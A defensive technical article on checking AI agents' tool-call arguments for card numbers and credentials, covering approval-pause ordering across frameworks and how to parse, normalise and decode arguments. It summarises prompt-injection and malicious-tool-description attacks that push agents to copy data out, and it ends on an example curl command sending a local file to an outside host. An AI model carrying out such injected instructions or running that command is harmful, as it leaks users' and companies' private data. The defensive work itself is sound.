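# Scanning an AI agent's proposed tool calls for card numbers and credentials before they run

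## How sensitive data gets into a tool call

An AI agent is a program in which a language model uses tools to work through a task. A tool is a function that the surrounding software can run, for example to look up an order, search the web or send an email. To use a tool, the model produces a tool call, which is a structured request that names the function and supplies the values to run it with, called arguments. When the tool sends email, whatever the model has written into the arguments goes to the recipient.

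Companies often have the software hold such calls until a person approves them. During that wait, a guard, which is code that inspects the proposed call, can check the arguments for data that should not go out. This check is well suited to payment card numbers, which the card industry's rules call primary account numbers (PANs), and credentials, which are secrets that grant access, such as passwords, API keys, access tokens and private keys. Both often have a form that software can recognise, and a stranger who receives either one may be able to use it at once.

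This problem has become more pressing as agents have moved from reading to acting. Stein, in *How are AI agents used?* (2026), collected 177,436 public tools built for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools and data. Tools that change an outside environment rose from 27% to 65% of tool usage between November 2024 and February 2026, according to the summary of Stein's work in *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications* (2026). A card number in the wrong field does harm when the tool is outbound, meaning that its arguments reach a party outside the system, as in an email, a web request or a public comment. Not all of the tools in that 65% are outbound.

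### One turn of an agent

For example, a customer named Dana asks a small software company's customer-support agent why her payment failed. One of the agent's turns then goes as follows.

1. The agent runtime, which is the software around the model, sends Dana's message to the model along with a list of tools. Each entry has a name, a description in plain language and a schema that sets out which arguments the tool takes.
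2. The model generates a response. This can be an answer in text or, where the task needs information or an action, a tool call.
3. The proposed tool call arrives at the runtime as data. So far nothing has happened in the world.
4. The runtime matches the name to a function and applies whatever checks its developers have built in. For some tools it starts an approval pause: it holds the call until a reviewer, the person in charge of that decision, approves or rejects it.
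5. The runtime runs the function with the given arguments. For an email, this is the point after which nobody can take the text back.
6. The runtime sends the function's result to the model, which generates another tool call or a final answer.

OpenAI's developer guide *Function calling* describes much the same loop in five steps and notes that it can repeat for as many calls as the task requires. Anthropic's *How tool use works* says that the model "never runs anything on its own." A guard is possible because there is always some software between the model's request and its effect, and for most tools that software belongs to the company that deploys the agent.

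Dana's question takes the agent round the loop twice. First the model calls a function named get_ticket, and the result is her whole support ticket. In one of her earlier messages Dana had typed out her card number. Further down, in an internal note, an engineer had pasted the API key of the company's billing service while fixing a fault. (An API key is a string that a program presents to show that it may use a service.) With all of this in front of it, the model proposes a second call:

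```json
{
  "id": "call_0017",
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "to": "dana@example.com",
    "subject": "Your failed payment",
    "body": "Hi Dana, your payment with card 4111 1111 1111 1111 failed because our billing service was down. We restored it using the key exk_live_7hQ2mV9xTz4LpR8sWc3NbY6k. Please try again."
  }
}
```

The card number is a test number that payment companies publish, and the key is invented. The layout is also slightly simplified. OpenAI's interface delivers the arguments as a JSON string that the runtime has to decode first, while the format in Anthropic's *Handle tool calls* puts them in an object named "input".

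The email is polite and answers the question, but it also gives Dana a key to the company's billing service that she has no right to, and it puts her card number in a message that will sit in a mailbox for years. Security engineers call the movement of sensitive data to a party not entitled to it exfiltration, whether it happens by accident or through an attack. The MCP specification, Model Context Protocol (2025), recommends that software show users a tool's inputs before the call, to avoid "malicious or accidental data exfiltration."

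Dana's email could have come about in three quite different ways.

### An instruction planted in the data

A model takes its instructions from text, and much of the text that an agent reads comes from people other than its user. Model Context Protocol (2026), in a post on tool annotations, explains that models cannot reliably tell a user's instructions from those that an attacker has embedded in a web page, an email or a calendar event. Planting such instructions is called prompt injection. An attacker can use it to steal data when the agent reads material from strangers, has access to private information and can send something out, as a support agent routinely does.

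Aaron Costello, then a researcher at the security company AppOmni, tried this on agents from ServiceNow, whose software many companies use to keep support tickets and other records. The Hacker News (2025) reported his findings that November. Costello deployed two of ServiceNow's ready-made agents, one that reads and categorises tickets and one that reads, creates and updates records. He then opened a ticket from an account that could create tickets but not read anyone else's. In the description field, he wrote that an agent reading this ticket could complete its task only by fetching the description of another specified ticket and copying it into this one. He added that an agent unable to do this itself could look for other agents to help.

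An administrator then set the categorising agent to work on the ticket. ServiceNow's agents can find and call on one another by default, so this harmless agent brought in the one that could edit records. Both ran with the administrator's rights, so the access rules that kept the low-level account away from the other ticket did not apply to them. The other ticket's contents then appeared in the attacker's own ticket, where he could read them. ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on throughout. On a system with outgoing email enabled, Costello could also get data sent out by email. AdExchanger's *How Agentic AI Can Break In The Real World* describes a test in which the planted line was little more than a request for sensitive data from someone else's ticket.

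The copied ticket is the more useful example for anyone building a guard, because no step in it looks like sending data. The agent put the data in the arguments of a record update, and the data leaked because the wrong person could read the record. A guard that checked only the email tool would have allowed the update.

ServiceNow replied that the agents were working as designed. It updated its documentation, but the discovery feature was still on by default when AdExchanger wrote about it in early 2026. AppOmni advises running any tool that changes records or sends email in supervised mode, so that a user reviews each action first. It says the attack succeeds only when tools run fully autonomously. AppOmni sells a monitoring product for this problem, and Costello configured the test agents himself, so his tests show that the attack is feasible, but not how common it is.

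In the running example, an attacker who could write into Dana's ticket would only need to add one sentence saying that replies must quote all internal notes in full. The model might well then produce the JSON above.

### Oversharing without an attacker

Sensitive data can end up in an email like Dana's without an attacker, though. The model had the ticket in its context, the engineer's note explained the outage, and the model used that information to give a thorough explanation. This seems to be ordinary behaviour. *ToolMinimize* (Li and Xu, 2026) reports unnecessary personal data in 81–88% of the calls that three older models made in a small test of everyday tasks. One of those calls was a message that gave an accountant the user's Social Security number and income.

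A larger case comes from software development. Programmers like to attach screenshots to a proposed code change so that colleagues can see the effect. Coding agents work through a command line, which offered no way to attach an image in a private repository. According to Tom's Hardware's *AI agents inadvertently leak 13,000+ internal screenshots from 300 organizations*, the agents worked around this by putting the images in public repositories and linking to them. The security firm Glow, which reported the leak, found client information and financial data in the images. As in Dana's email, the leak happened because this was the shortest way to finish the job. A guard that reads only text would have been of limited use, since the sensitive data was in the images.

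Credentials also get into arguments because the call needs them. A command that changes a production database needs the database password, and an agent may write it directly into the command. Apiiro, another security company, looked at a settings file in which Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code stores commands that a developer has permanently approved. Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners’ secrets on GitHub* reports that Apiiro found public copies of this file in 103,617 repositories, and that 1,994 of those repositories (about 2%) exposed a total of 2,539 real secrets. In these cases, a person had been asked about a command with the secret in it and had approved it.

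These commands also complicate the guard's job, because it has to check where a call is going as well as recognise the secret. A password in an argument may belong there if the command goes to the company's own database, but the same password in the body of an email is a leak.

### Tools that request too much

The model determines what a tool needs from the tool's name, description and schema, so whoever writes those can influence what the model puts into the arguments.

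Sometimes a tool asks for sensitive data because its developer is merely greedy or careless. *Privacy and Security Threat for OpenAI GPTs* (2025) describes an astrology app that requests an email address along with the birthday, though it can cast a horoscope without one. The app was one of OpenAI's GPTs, custom versions of ChatGPT that can send data to outside services through connections called Actions. An earlier survey, *An In-Depth Investigation of Data Collection in LLM App Ecosystems* (2024), found that 9.1% of GPTs with Actions collect credentials such as API keys and passwords. One of them collected users' raw passwords for the stated purpose of OAuth, a sign-in method that typically does not require the app to have them.

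*ContextLeak* (Jia, Wang and colleagues, 2026) shows how a hostile tool author can steal an agent's context, that is, the user's request, the conversation so far or the list of installed tools. The researchers built tools whose names and descriptions lead an agent to pass this context along. The theft works only if the agent chooses the malicious tool and puts the context into the arguments, and the tool's code then forwards it. Earlier attacks concentrated on the choice of tool and the forwarding code, whereas Jia and colleagues focused on the arguments. They trained a language model to write tool descriptions and rewarded it when a test agent both picked the tool and copied the context accurately into the arguments.

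The resulting descriptions present the tool as a standard entry point for, for example, all email tasks, and complete input as a technical requirement for correct results, without ordering the agent to hand anything over. Agents running on several models often chose these tools and then copied much of their context into the input, in many cases nearly word for word. The attack was weaker against a commercial coding agent, which usually chose another tool. Detectors that screen tool descriptions for malicious text missed almost all of these descriptions, presumably because they contained so little objectionable wording.

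The experiments did not involve card numbers or keys, but a tool that receives the whole conversation receives everything the user typed, which in Dana's case included her card number. If the support company had installed an outside supplier's email tool, with a description stating that the body must contain the full ticket history for reliable delivery, the model would have had a reason to include both secrets. Jia and colleagues mention checking the arguments as a possible defence, but warn that tools often need context for legitimate purposes, so an overly strict filter will break working tools.

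Tool call arguments are a good place to look for sensitive data because a guard can detect it there regardless of how it got in. A defence against prompt injection won't stop a model from oversharing unprompted, and vetting the installed tools won't stop a model from acting on a sentence planted in a ticket. Whatever the cause, the card number 4111 1111 1111 1111 appears as the same sixteen digits in the body of the email.

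### Secrets that reach only the model provider

Some leaks attributed to agents never pass through an outbound tool's arguments, so a guard on those arguments will not catch them. TechRadar's *'I leaked secrets'* describes a case in which a quality-assurance engineer asked an AI coding assistant to examine some proposed software changes. The project's instructions pointed the assistant to an access token in a configuration file that also held production passwords, a token for the internal human-resources system and credentials for a business-intelligence service. The assistant read the entire file in 10 separate sessions over three weeks, and each time the contents went to the external AI service behind it. In a fresh copy of the project without that file, it retrieved all of the computer's environment variables, which are settings that programs share, and exposed more passwords.

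This account comes from NordLayer, a security vendor that says its AI Scout product observed the sessions. TechRadar's *'What companies are facing today is an AI zoo'* describes AI Scout as a tool that monitors employees' use of AI and warns about, redacts or blocks sensitive prompts. NordLayer therefore has a commercial interest in the story, and the article does not name the affected company or cite anyone else who confirmed the account. The mechanism is plausible, though, since agents normally work this way.

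The secrets moved in step 6 of the turn described above, when the runtime sent a tool's result to the model. A guard that inspected the arguments of the call to read the file would have found no password, because those arguments need to contain little more than the file's location. The same thing happened in Dana's case, before anyone considered sending an email. Once get_ticket had returned the ticket, her card number and the billing key were on their way to whichever company runs the model.

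How serious this exposure is depends on the provider, the contract and what the provider stores. It calls for different measures than an email to an outsider does, such as keeping credentials in a vault instead of in files that the agent reads, or removing them from tool results before the model receives them. Keeping a secret out of the model's context also makes it much less likely to appear in a tool call, because a secret in the context can turn up in the arguments of any later call in that session.

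## Where to place the check, and whether the approval pause is the last chance

A company can inspect data at six points in an agent's turn: the user's message, retrieved content, tool results, tool call arguments, the final answer, and the network. The table shows Dana's case at each point, assuming the agent tells her in the chat once the email has gone out.

| Checkpoint | What passes through it in Dana's case | Card number or billing key |
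|---|---|---|
| User input | Her question about the failed payment | Neither |
| Retrieved content | A help article on failed payments, if the system adds one to the prompt | Neither |
| Tool results | The ticket from get_ticket, and later a delivery confirmation from send_email | Both, in the ticket |
| Tool arguments | The recipient, subject and body of the proposed email | Both |
| Final answer | A line telling Dana to check her inbox | Neither |
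| Network | The request to the mail service | Both, usually encrypted |

A check on tool results would be the better fix for the billing key, since no reply to a customer needs it. But the agent may have a good reason to hold the card number, such as finding the matching payment, and when get_ticket returns the ticket, nobody knows yet where its contents will go. The proposed tool call's arguments are the first place where the data appears together with its destination.

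Companies that route model traffic through a gateway can check tool calls slightly earlier. A gateway is a server between the runtime and the model provider, so it receives the model's response before the runtime does. LiteLLM's *Tool Permission Guardrail* describes a gateway that allows or denies tool calls using rules on the tool's name. A rule on names alone would let Dana's email through, because the agent is supposed to use send_email.

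### Why checks on the question and the answer miss the email

In a plain chatbot, data comes in only through the question and goes out only through the answer, so checking both covers the whole exchange. An agent can also send data out through its tools, which those checks do not cover.

According to AWS's *Extend Amazon Bedrock Guardrails to Tool Interactions Using the Strands Agents SDK*, AWS's standard Bedrock guardrails check the prompt before the model runs and the response afterwards, but nothing validates the parameters the model chooses for the tool calls in between. AWS sells the guardrail service that it recommends for closing this gap, but other vendors describe the same gap in their own software. According to Pydantic's *Input, Output & Tool Guardrails*, the input guard in its agent framework screens only the user's prompt, on the first model request of a run. Tool arguments and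 results pass unchecked unless the developer adds a separate tool guard.

The gap widens when several agents share the work. Suppose a reception agent passes Dana's question to a billing agent, which sends the email and hands control back to the reception agent to write the closing line. In OpenAI's Agents SDK, a kit for building agents in Python or JavaScript, input guardrails run only for the first agent in the chain, and output guardrails run only for the agent that produces the final answer. Neither kind would run for the billing agent. OpenAI's *Guardrails and human review* therefore advises developers to put validation next to the tool that creates the side effect.

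A guardrail can also run too late to stop a tool call. OpenAI's *Guardrails* explains that input guardrails run in parallel with the agent by default to save time, so the agent may already have run tools when a guardrail stops the request. Developers can turn off parallel mode to make the agent wait. An output guardrail always runs too late because it checks the agent's final answer, which comes after tool calls such as sending an email.

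Filters on retrieved content also leave a tool call's arguments unchecked. Zhang and Pei (2026), in *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data*, report that agents built on a deliberately tampered model could leak user data through tool calls despite such filters. The attack requires a company to install the tampered model and give it both stored user data and broad outbound access, so the result is weak evidence of how often ordinary agents leak. It does show that filtering incoming text is not always enough to stop data from leaving in a tool call. A guard on the arguments checks the outgoing request, but it still has to recognise the data, which an attacker may disguise.

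### Whether the argument check runs before or after the pause

A guard can run before the approval pause, after it, or both. If it runs only after approval, the reviewer has to spot the key in Dana's email unaided, and if it runs only before, nothing inspects a change that someone makes during the review. Agent frameworks differ on when the guard runs, and their documentation is not always explicit.

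Pydantic AI is a Python framework whose ready-made guards come in a companion package, Pydantic AI Harness. The package was still on 0.x releases in late 2026, and Pydantic warns that its interface may change between minor versions. Its ToolGuardrail passes the validated arguments to a function the developer chooses just before the tool runs. This function can hold the call for approval, which puts the steps in a good order. The guard scans the email and then requests approval, and the run ends with a list of held calls. When the application starts a follow-up run with the reviewer's answer, the guard runs again and can still block a call that the reviewer has approved.

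A developer can also require approval by marking a tool with requires_approval=True, rather than through the guard. This seems to put approval before the scan. Pydantic states that the framework hands deferred calls back to the application before any execution hook runs (a hook is a function that the framework calls at a set point). Pydantic's *Deferred Tools* includes tools that need approval among the deferred ones. Together, the two guides imply that if send_email were marked this way, the reviewer would see Dana's email unscanned, and the guard would scan it only after approval.

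There are several ways to get a scan in earlier:

- The developer can leave the mark off and have the guard itself ask for approval.
- A tool can have an args_validator, a function that can reject arguments before anyone asks a person to approve them.
- The application can scan the list of held calls before it displays them.
- A handler inside the run can receive the held calls and deny some of them in code.

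Pydantic notes that the framework sends held calls to its event stream before any handler runs, so that an interface can show the user that input is needed. A review screen that displays calls straight from this stream would show the arguments before the handler had scanned them.

Pydantic does not specify whether an output guard receives a paused run. The run does end with a kind of output, a DeferredToolRequests object that contains the held calls. But the package's ready-made secret detectors work only on text. Their output versions raise an error on anything that is not a string, or skip it if the developer chooses that setting, so the body of the email is not scanned in either case.

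OpenAI's documentation is less clear about the order. The Python kit's main tool decorator has supported tool guardrails since version 0.6.5, according to the release notes reproduced in *pypi openai-agents 0.6.5*. OpenAI says that a tool's input guardrails run before the tool executes. OpenAI's *Human-in-the-loop* says that the kit evaluates a tool's approval rule when the call is about to execute, and that a call awaiting approval does not execute. Neither guide states which comes first. The wording suggests that approval comes first, in which case the guardrail would not check Dana's email until the run resumes.

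That is not enough evidence to base a security control on, but a developer can settle the question with a short test. The developer can give send_email both an approval rule and a guardrail, have the agent propose an email with a test card number, and check whether the guardrail has logged anything by the time the run pauses. The test needs repeating after upgrades. OpenAI's *Release process/changelog* says the leading zero in the Python kit's version number means the kit is still evolving rapidly, and minor versions can include breaking changes.

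Developers can also run the scan inside the approval rule, so that it doesn't matter whether the approval pause is the last chance. The rule can be a function that reads the tool call's arguments. OpenAI's example is a rule for a sendEmail tool that holds any message whose subject contains the word "spam", and a scan for card numbers and keys fits in the same place. The function can return only "yes" or "no" to whether the call needs approval, so the developer has to store the findings somewhere else for the reviewer. If it returns "no" for a clean email, the email goes out without review, so a company that wants a person to approve every email should have the function scan and then always return "yes".

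Output guardrails in OpenAI's kit check the final answer. A paused run does not have one yet and instead returns a list of pending approvals and a saved state from which the application can resume. An output guardrail would presumably run only after the agent had resumed and finished, when the email would already be in Dana's inbox.

The AI SDK, Vercel's toolkit for building AI applications in TypeScript, has the simplest arrangement of these frameworks. AI SDK's *Tool Approvals* describes a setting called toolApproval, which can be a function that receives a call's parsed input and decides whether to run the call, deny it or ask the user. A scan in this function runs before the user is asked. It runs again when the application continues after an approval, because the SDK then checks the input against the tool's schema and re-evaluates the approval policy. If the policy now denies the call,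 it does not run, despite the user's approval. The second evaluation also matters because, in the standard chat setup, the user's browser sends back the conversation history, including the approval, which could be forged unless the developer has turned on signing.

Strands Agents, the framework in AWS's example, triggers an event before each tool call. In the example, a hook attached to this event checks the call's parameters and can cancel the call. Approval uses the same event. According to Strands Agents, this is the only event at which a hook can interrupt a run, and the hook runs again with the person's response when the run resumes. A hook that scans the parameters before interrupting will therefore scan them again after approval.

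Strands also has a ready-made approval handler, described in Strands Agents' *Human in the Loop*. Classmethod's *I tried out the Human in the Loop handler for Strands Agents* ran it with version 1.46.0 of the Python package. The approval handler and a separate scanning handler can interfere with each other. A handler that denies a call stops the remaining handlers from running, according to Strands Agents, and a handler can also edit a call's content before execution. If a handler edited the call after approval, the agent would send something other than what the reviewer approved.

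The same problem is easier to see in Dapr, an open-source runtime for distributed applications with its own agent framework. Dapr's *Hooks and Human-in-the-Loop* explicitly states that hooks run in the order the developer registered them, and that the framework skips the rest after the first one that decides anything other than "proceed". If the approval hook comes first, it pauses the call and the reviewer sees it unscanned. Putting the scan first fixes this for emails with no secrets. But a scan that finds the billing key and replaces it with a placeholder changes the arguments, which also counts as a decision other than "proceed". By the documented rule, Dapr would then skip the approval hook and send the edited email without review. Scanning and asking for approval within a single hook avoids both problems.

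### Calls that the argument check does not cover

Getting the order right helps only with calls that pass through the check, and each framework has some that don't. OpenAI has the longest list of tools whose calls bypass it. *Guardrails*, the guide for its Python kit, lists them by name as of spring 2026.

| Framework | Calls outside its argument check |
|---|---|
| Pydantic AI (ToolGuardrail) | Tools that the application runs itself; tools that run at the model provider, such as web search; output tools, which produce the agent's structured answer |
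| OpenAI Agents SDK (tool guardrails) | Hosted web search, file search, code interpreter, image generation and MCP tools; built-in computer, shell and file-patching tools; handoffs between agents |
| AI SDK (toolApproval) | Tools that run at the provider; tools of subagents |

The gap is easy to close when the company's own application runs the tool. Pydantic says the check belongs in the application because the application executes the call. Web searches run by the model provider are harder to check. For example, the billing service might return an error message that includes an invalid key, and the agent might search the web for that message without removing the key. The search runs on the provider's servers as part of the model's response, so the company's runtime receives the query only afterwards, if at all.

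OpenAI's shell tool runs commands that can carry passwords or upload files, so it needs a guard at least as much as the email tool does. The guardrails do not cover it, but a local shell can have an approval rule or a callback that approves or rejects in code. Hosted shell environments support neither, according to *Human-in-the-loop*, the Python kit's approval guide.

Ordinary configuration leaves further gaps. ToolGuardrail covers every tool by default, but a developer can restrict it to a list of names. If a name is misspelled, the intended tool is left unguarded, and the only sign is a warning when a run completes successfully, when the email may already have been sent. The developer also has to guess which tools can leak data, and few developers would have listed the record update from the ServiceNow test. It seems safer to scan the arguments of every tool and exempt a tool only for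 a reason.

### Is the pause the last chance to stop the data?

Software can still keep data from leaving after a person has approved a tool call, although developers often treat approval as the final safeguard. In Dana's case, the person's chance to decide ends with a click on "approve", but the data doesn't leave until send_email passes the message to the mail service. Depending on the runtime, a good deal of code can run in between.

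The approval pause is the last chance to scan a tool call when the application runs the approved call without another check. This happens with tools that Pydantic AI hands back to the application, and in any agent with a custom loop that calls the function as soon as the approval arrives. If the guard has not scanned an email before the reviewer approves it, the application will send it unscanned.

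When the developer requires approval for hosted MCP tools in OpenAI's kit, the approval request is also the company's only chance to inspect the arguments before execution, because these tools run from OpenAI's servers, outside the guardrail pipeline. OpenAI lets the application attach a callback that makes the approval decision in code instead of asking a person, and a guard could run there.

A hook at execution can check the call after the approval pause, so calling the pause the last chance is too strong. Pydantic AI runs its guard again on the resumed run, the AI SDK evaluates its policy again, and a Strands hook executes a second time. If the reviewer overlooks the billing key and approves, software can still block the email. A developer can get the same protection in any framework by putting a scan at the top of the send_email function, since every call to it will then be scanned. A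 filter on outgoing network traffic can run even later. The reviewer gets another chance to decide only if the code that stops the email also sends it back for review.

The claim that the approval pause is the last chance to check a call fails for tools that run without approval, since they have no pause. These include provider-run web search, and hosted MCP servers if the developer has set approval to "never", which *Human-in-the-loop* suggests for trusted servers. The company then has to act before the model makes the call. It can keep secrets out of the context or withhold the tool from the model. It can also replace the hosted tool with its own equivalent function, so that a guard can check the arguments.

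A tool can also have an approval rule and still run without a pause. To reduce the number of prompts, frameworks let reviewers answer once for many calls. In OpenAI's kit, a reviewer's decision can apply to every later call to the same tool in that run. In the Strands Agents handler, a developer can allow the answer "trust", which approves the current call and skips the prompt for that tool for the rest of the session. If a reviewer trusts send_email after a harmless first message, they won't be asked about a later message in that session that contains a key. The guard should therefore run whether or not a call will pause.

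Holding one call does not necessarily hold the others the model proposes with it. In an example from Pydantic's guide, the model requests three file operations at once. Two wait for approval, while the third runs immediately. If the model proposed the email to Dana together with a web request containing the same text, and only the email needed approval, the web request could go out while the reviewer was still reading.

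The approval request itself can also leak data before the reviewer decides. Reviewers need to see a tool's inputs, as the MCP specification recommends, but they don't always view them on a secure internal screen. Strands Agents lists Slack messages and push notifications among the ways to ask for approval. Its prompt describes the tool call, and the command-line version includes the input. If the support company sent prompts containing the full arguments to Slack, Dana's card number and the billing key would be in a channel before anyone had made a decision, even if the reviewer then stopped the email.

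### Scanning before review and again before execution

The guard should scan each call before the reviewer sees it and again just before the tool runs. The first scan gives the reviewer the findings and lets the application mask secrets in the approval request. The second covers anything that has changed since.

Arguments can change after the first scan. In Pydantic AI, the reviewer's answer can include replacement arguments. Suppose the reviewer deletes the billing key from Dana's email but pastes in a line from the ticket that contains her card's security code. The runtime will send the reviewer's version, which the earlier scan did not cover. Other software can change the arguments too, so the later scan should run after all of it. For this reason, Pydantic places its tool guard last among the hooks that handle arguments.

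The later scan also needs to know what the reviewer has already seen. Otherwise it will find a card number that the reviewer knowingly approved and stop the email again. In outline, for a call that needs approval:

```python
seen = scan(call.arguments)
review = ask_reviewer(call, seen)

if review.approved:
    new = scan(review.arguments) - seen
    if new:
        hold_again(call, review.arguments, new)
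    else:
        run_tool(call.name, review.arguments)
```

Here `scan` returns a set of pairs, each containing a sensitive value and the field it appears in, so the subtraction leaves only the values that the reviewer added or moved to another field. For a call that does not need approval, the same scan runs once, immediately before the tool runs.

Frameworks do not make this comparison automatically. In Pydantic AI, once a person has approved a call, a guard can still block it, but asking for approval again has no effect. A guard that asks for approval whenever it finds a secret would therefore catch the original key but let through the security code that the reviewer pasted in. When the run resumes, the guard has to block new findings.

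Running the scan twice takes little compute if it uses pattern matching on the company's own machines. AWS suggests a lightweight local check like this for tool parameters, as an alternative to its hosted guardrail. Scanning locally also avoids sending the arguments, with any card numbers or credentials in them, to another service.

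## Reading the arguments completely

Detectors search text, but a tool call's arguments are structured data. A card number can be nested several levels deep, placed in a field's name instead of its value, or encoded. The guard first has to turn the arguments into a list of plain strings and record where each one came from.

### Walking the whole structure

Some guards check only the fields that a developer names. *Argument Validation*, the guide to the JavaScript library ai-tool-guard, gives the example `piiGuard("query")`, which scans one field for card numbers and other personal data. A check like this on the body of Dana's email would find her card number there but miss it in the subject line. If someone later renamed the field from `body` to `content`, the check would probably find nothing, because most of the library's ready-made guards allow a call when the field is missing. The library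 also has a wildcard for checking the whole arguments object, which suits leak detection better.

Another shortcut is to scan the arguments as one long JSON string. cdot65's *prisma-airs-tool-guard* describes a plug-in that serialises a call's parameters this way and sends the string to a scanning service. The string includes every name and value, including numbers, but JSON can write the same text in more than one way. *The JavaScript Object Notation (JSON) Data Interchange Format* (Bray, 2017), the internet standard for JSON, allows any character to be written as an escape sequence, so `\u0034111` means 4111. Parsing and re-serialising the JSON removes most such escapes, but a line break in a private key still comes out as `\n`. The guard also can't tell from the match alone which field it came from.

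It is more reliable to parse the JSON once and visit everything in it:

```python
def read_arguments(raw):
    args = parse_json(raw)          # once; on any error, hold the call
    texts = []                      # pairs of (path, text)

    def walk(node, path):
        if is_object(node):
            for name, value in node.items():
                texts.append((path + [name, "(name)"], name))
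                walk(value, path + [name])
        elif is_list(node):
            for i, item in enumerate(node):
                walk(item, path + [i])
        elif is_string(node):
            texts.append((path, node))
        elif is_number(node):
            texts.append((path, plain_digits(node)))

    walk(args, [])
    return args, texts
```

The function returns `args` as well as the texts because the tool has to run with that same object later.

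The walk includes names because some tools accept objects with free-form names, such as custom headers for a web request, and a model can write a card number there. OpenAI's strict mode largely prevents this by making calls follow the tool's schema and requiring the schema to forbid additional names. But OpenAI currently disables strict mode when a fine-tuned model makes several calls in one turn, so checking the names is still worthwhile.

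A card number may arrive as an integer, without quotation marks. JSON also permits exponents, so `4.111111111111111e15` is Dana's card number, and `plain_digits` has to write it out in full. Many parsers store numbers in a format that is exact only up to 2^53 − 1, or 9,007,199,254,740,991. A sixteen-digit card number fits under that limit if it starts with 6 or less, but some card numbers have up to 19 digits. Python's parser keeps integers exact, but JavaScript's built-in parser may change the last few digits of a number that long, and a detector that tests the card checksum would then probably reject it.

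OpenAI's custom tools take free text instead of JSON, and the guard can treat that text as a single string. The guard should hold any call whose arguments arrive in a form it does not expect. Arcjet's *OpenAI Agents agent guard* describes a guard that warns when it receives neither a string nor an object, since it has then scanned no arguments. A warning alone would not stop Dana's email. A small package on PyPI, the public index of Python software, handles this more safely by blocking any call whose payload it cannot parse.

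### Normalising the text

The same card number can be written in different ways. Normalisation converts these variants to one form so that the detectors need fewer patterns. The guard should normalise copies of each string and scan the original too, because a change that helps find card numbers can damage a key.

Unicode's standard procedure for this, NFKC, turns the full-width digits common in East Asian text into ordinary ones, and non-breaking spaces into normal spaces. It doesn't change Arabic-Indic digits, dashes or invisible zero-width spaces, so the guard has to convert or remove those itself. The guard can then delete single spaces and hyphens between digits, which turns 4111 1111 1111 1111 into 4111111111111111. It should keep hyphens elsewhere, since they may be part of a key.

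Pydantic's ready-made card detector handles this step in the pattern instead, accepting the digits in any grouping. Pydantic's private-key detector accepts both real line breaks and the two characters `\n`. Those two characters can remain after JSON parsing if the model copied the key from a settings file that stored it that way.

### Decoding to a fixed depth and size

Encodings hide data more thoroughly. Base64, for example, represents any data using 64 common characters, and programs routinely use it for attachments and settings. Leon's *Secret Scanning Encoded and Archived Data* describes the decoders in TruffleHog, a tool that searches files for credentials. Amazon access keys often begin with AKIA, which becomes QUtJQ in base64. A search for QUtJQ on the code-hosting site GitHub returned over 4,000 results, most of them invalid keys but some live.

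Base64 converts three bytes at a time, so the same key looks different if it starts in the middle of a group of three. A guard that only added QUtJQ to its patterns would miss some encoded keys. TruffleHog instead picks out every stretch of text that looks like base64, tries to decode it and searches the result.

Gitleaks, an open-source scanner for code repositories, also decodes hexadecimal and percent-encoding (the form in which a space in a web address becomes `%20`). It repeats this on its own output until nothing is left to decode or it reaches a depth set by the user. The default depth is zero, so decoding is off unless the user turns it on. Mondoo's *Decoding and Validating Secrets* also describes decoding as optional and off by default, although it notes that people often commit secrets under one layer of encoding. According to Gitleaks, decoding barely increases scan time, so a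 guard on tool calls has little reason to leave it off.

Gitleaks's limits need adjusting for this job. It decodes hexadecimal strings only if they have at least 32 characters, and base64 strings only if they have at least 16. A sixteen-digit card number takes exactly 32 characters in hexadecimal, but a fifteen-digit American Express number takes 30, and an eight-character password takes 12 in base64, so Gitleaks would miss both. According to a comment in the decoder's source code, Debian's *base64.go*, it also misses about 1% of base64 data in order to avoid trying to decode long names in program code. An email contains far less text than a repository, so a guard can use lower limits and leave out this shortcut.

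Gitleaks avoids many false alarms by keeping decoded text only if it is all printable ASCII, the basic English character set. In one of the project's tests, Debian's *decoder_test.go*, Gitleaks leaves a forty-character hexadecimal string that looks like a version identifier unchanged, but it decodes another into a readable password. The rule also rejects text in UTF-16, a format that uses at least two bytes per character. Windows' PowerShell accepts whole commands as base64-encoded UTF-16, so a guard for an agent that runs such commands should try that format too.

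The guard needs limits on depth and size, because otherwise an attacker could stall it with a small compressed file that expands to gigabytes. A limit of three layers and a megabyte of decoded text seems generous for an email. If a value exceeds either limit, the guard should report it as unread, because skipping it silently would let an attacker hide a key behind padding.

Each decoded string should keep the path and position of the encoded text it came from, along with the encoding and depth, as in Gitleaks' findings. Otherwise the guard could report a key in Dana's email but not remove it.

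### Dana's email before and after

In the original email, the walk produces three names, `to`, `subject` and `body`, and their values. Both secrets are in the `body` value. Normalisation removes the separators from the card number and leaves the billing key unchanged.

Suppose the email tool also took a set of template fields and a list of links, and the model used them:

```json
{
  "to": "dana@example.com",
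  "subject": "Your failed payment",
  "body": "Hi Dana, your payment with card 4111 1111 1111 1111 failed.",
  "fields": { "card": 4111111111111111 },
  "links": [
    "https://status.example.com/?ref=ZXhrX2xpdmVfN2hRMm1WOXhUejRMcFI4c1djM05iWTZr"
  ]
}
```

| Path | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| `body` | 4111 1111 1111 1111 | 4111111111111111 |
| `fields.card` | 4111111111111111, as a number | 4111111111111111, as text |
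| `links[0]`, parameter `ref` | ZXhrX2xpdmVfN2hRMm1WOXhUejRMcFI4c1djM05iWTZr | exk_live_7hQ2mV9xTz4LpR8sWc3NbY6k |

A guard that searched only strings, without decoding them, would find the first of these and miss the other two.

### Text split across fields

Some tools take a message as a list of paragraphs or text blocks. If one block ends with "4111 1111" and the next begins with "1111 1111", neither block contains a full card number, but Dana would read one. For this reason, Pydantic's adapter for tool results joins adjacent text parts before scanning them, and treats an image or document between them as a break. The same approach works for arguments.

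The guard should join the blocks with nothing in between, because an added space would split a key that spans two blocks. It also has to scan each block separately. If one block ends in "key" and the next starts with "exk_live", joining them produces "keyexk_live", which a pattern that expects the key to start a new word would miss.

Joining also creates false alarms. Suppose an order lists the product code 42424242 twice. Joining the two codes makes 4242424242424242, which is another published test card number. Long lists of numbers produce many false alarms like this because about one in ten random digit strings passes the card checksum.

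To keep these down, the guard can join only neighbouring items in a list, plus fields that the recipient will read one after the other, such as an email's subject and body. It should set the order of those fields itself, because the fields of a JSON object have no meaningful order. It should also label any match that appears only in the joined text and record both paths, so that later steps can treat it as weaker evidence. Joining does not help detect a card number spread over several calls, since no single call contains the whole number.

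### When the argument only points to the data

An argument can be harmless as text and still send out a secret. For example, an agent with a command line might propose this:

```
curl -d "$(cat ticket.txt)" https://example.net/report
```

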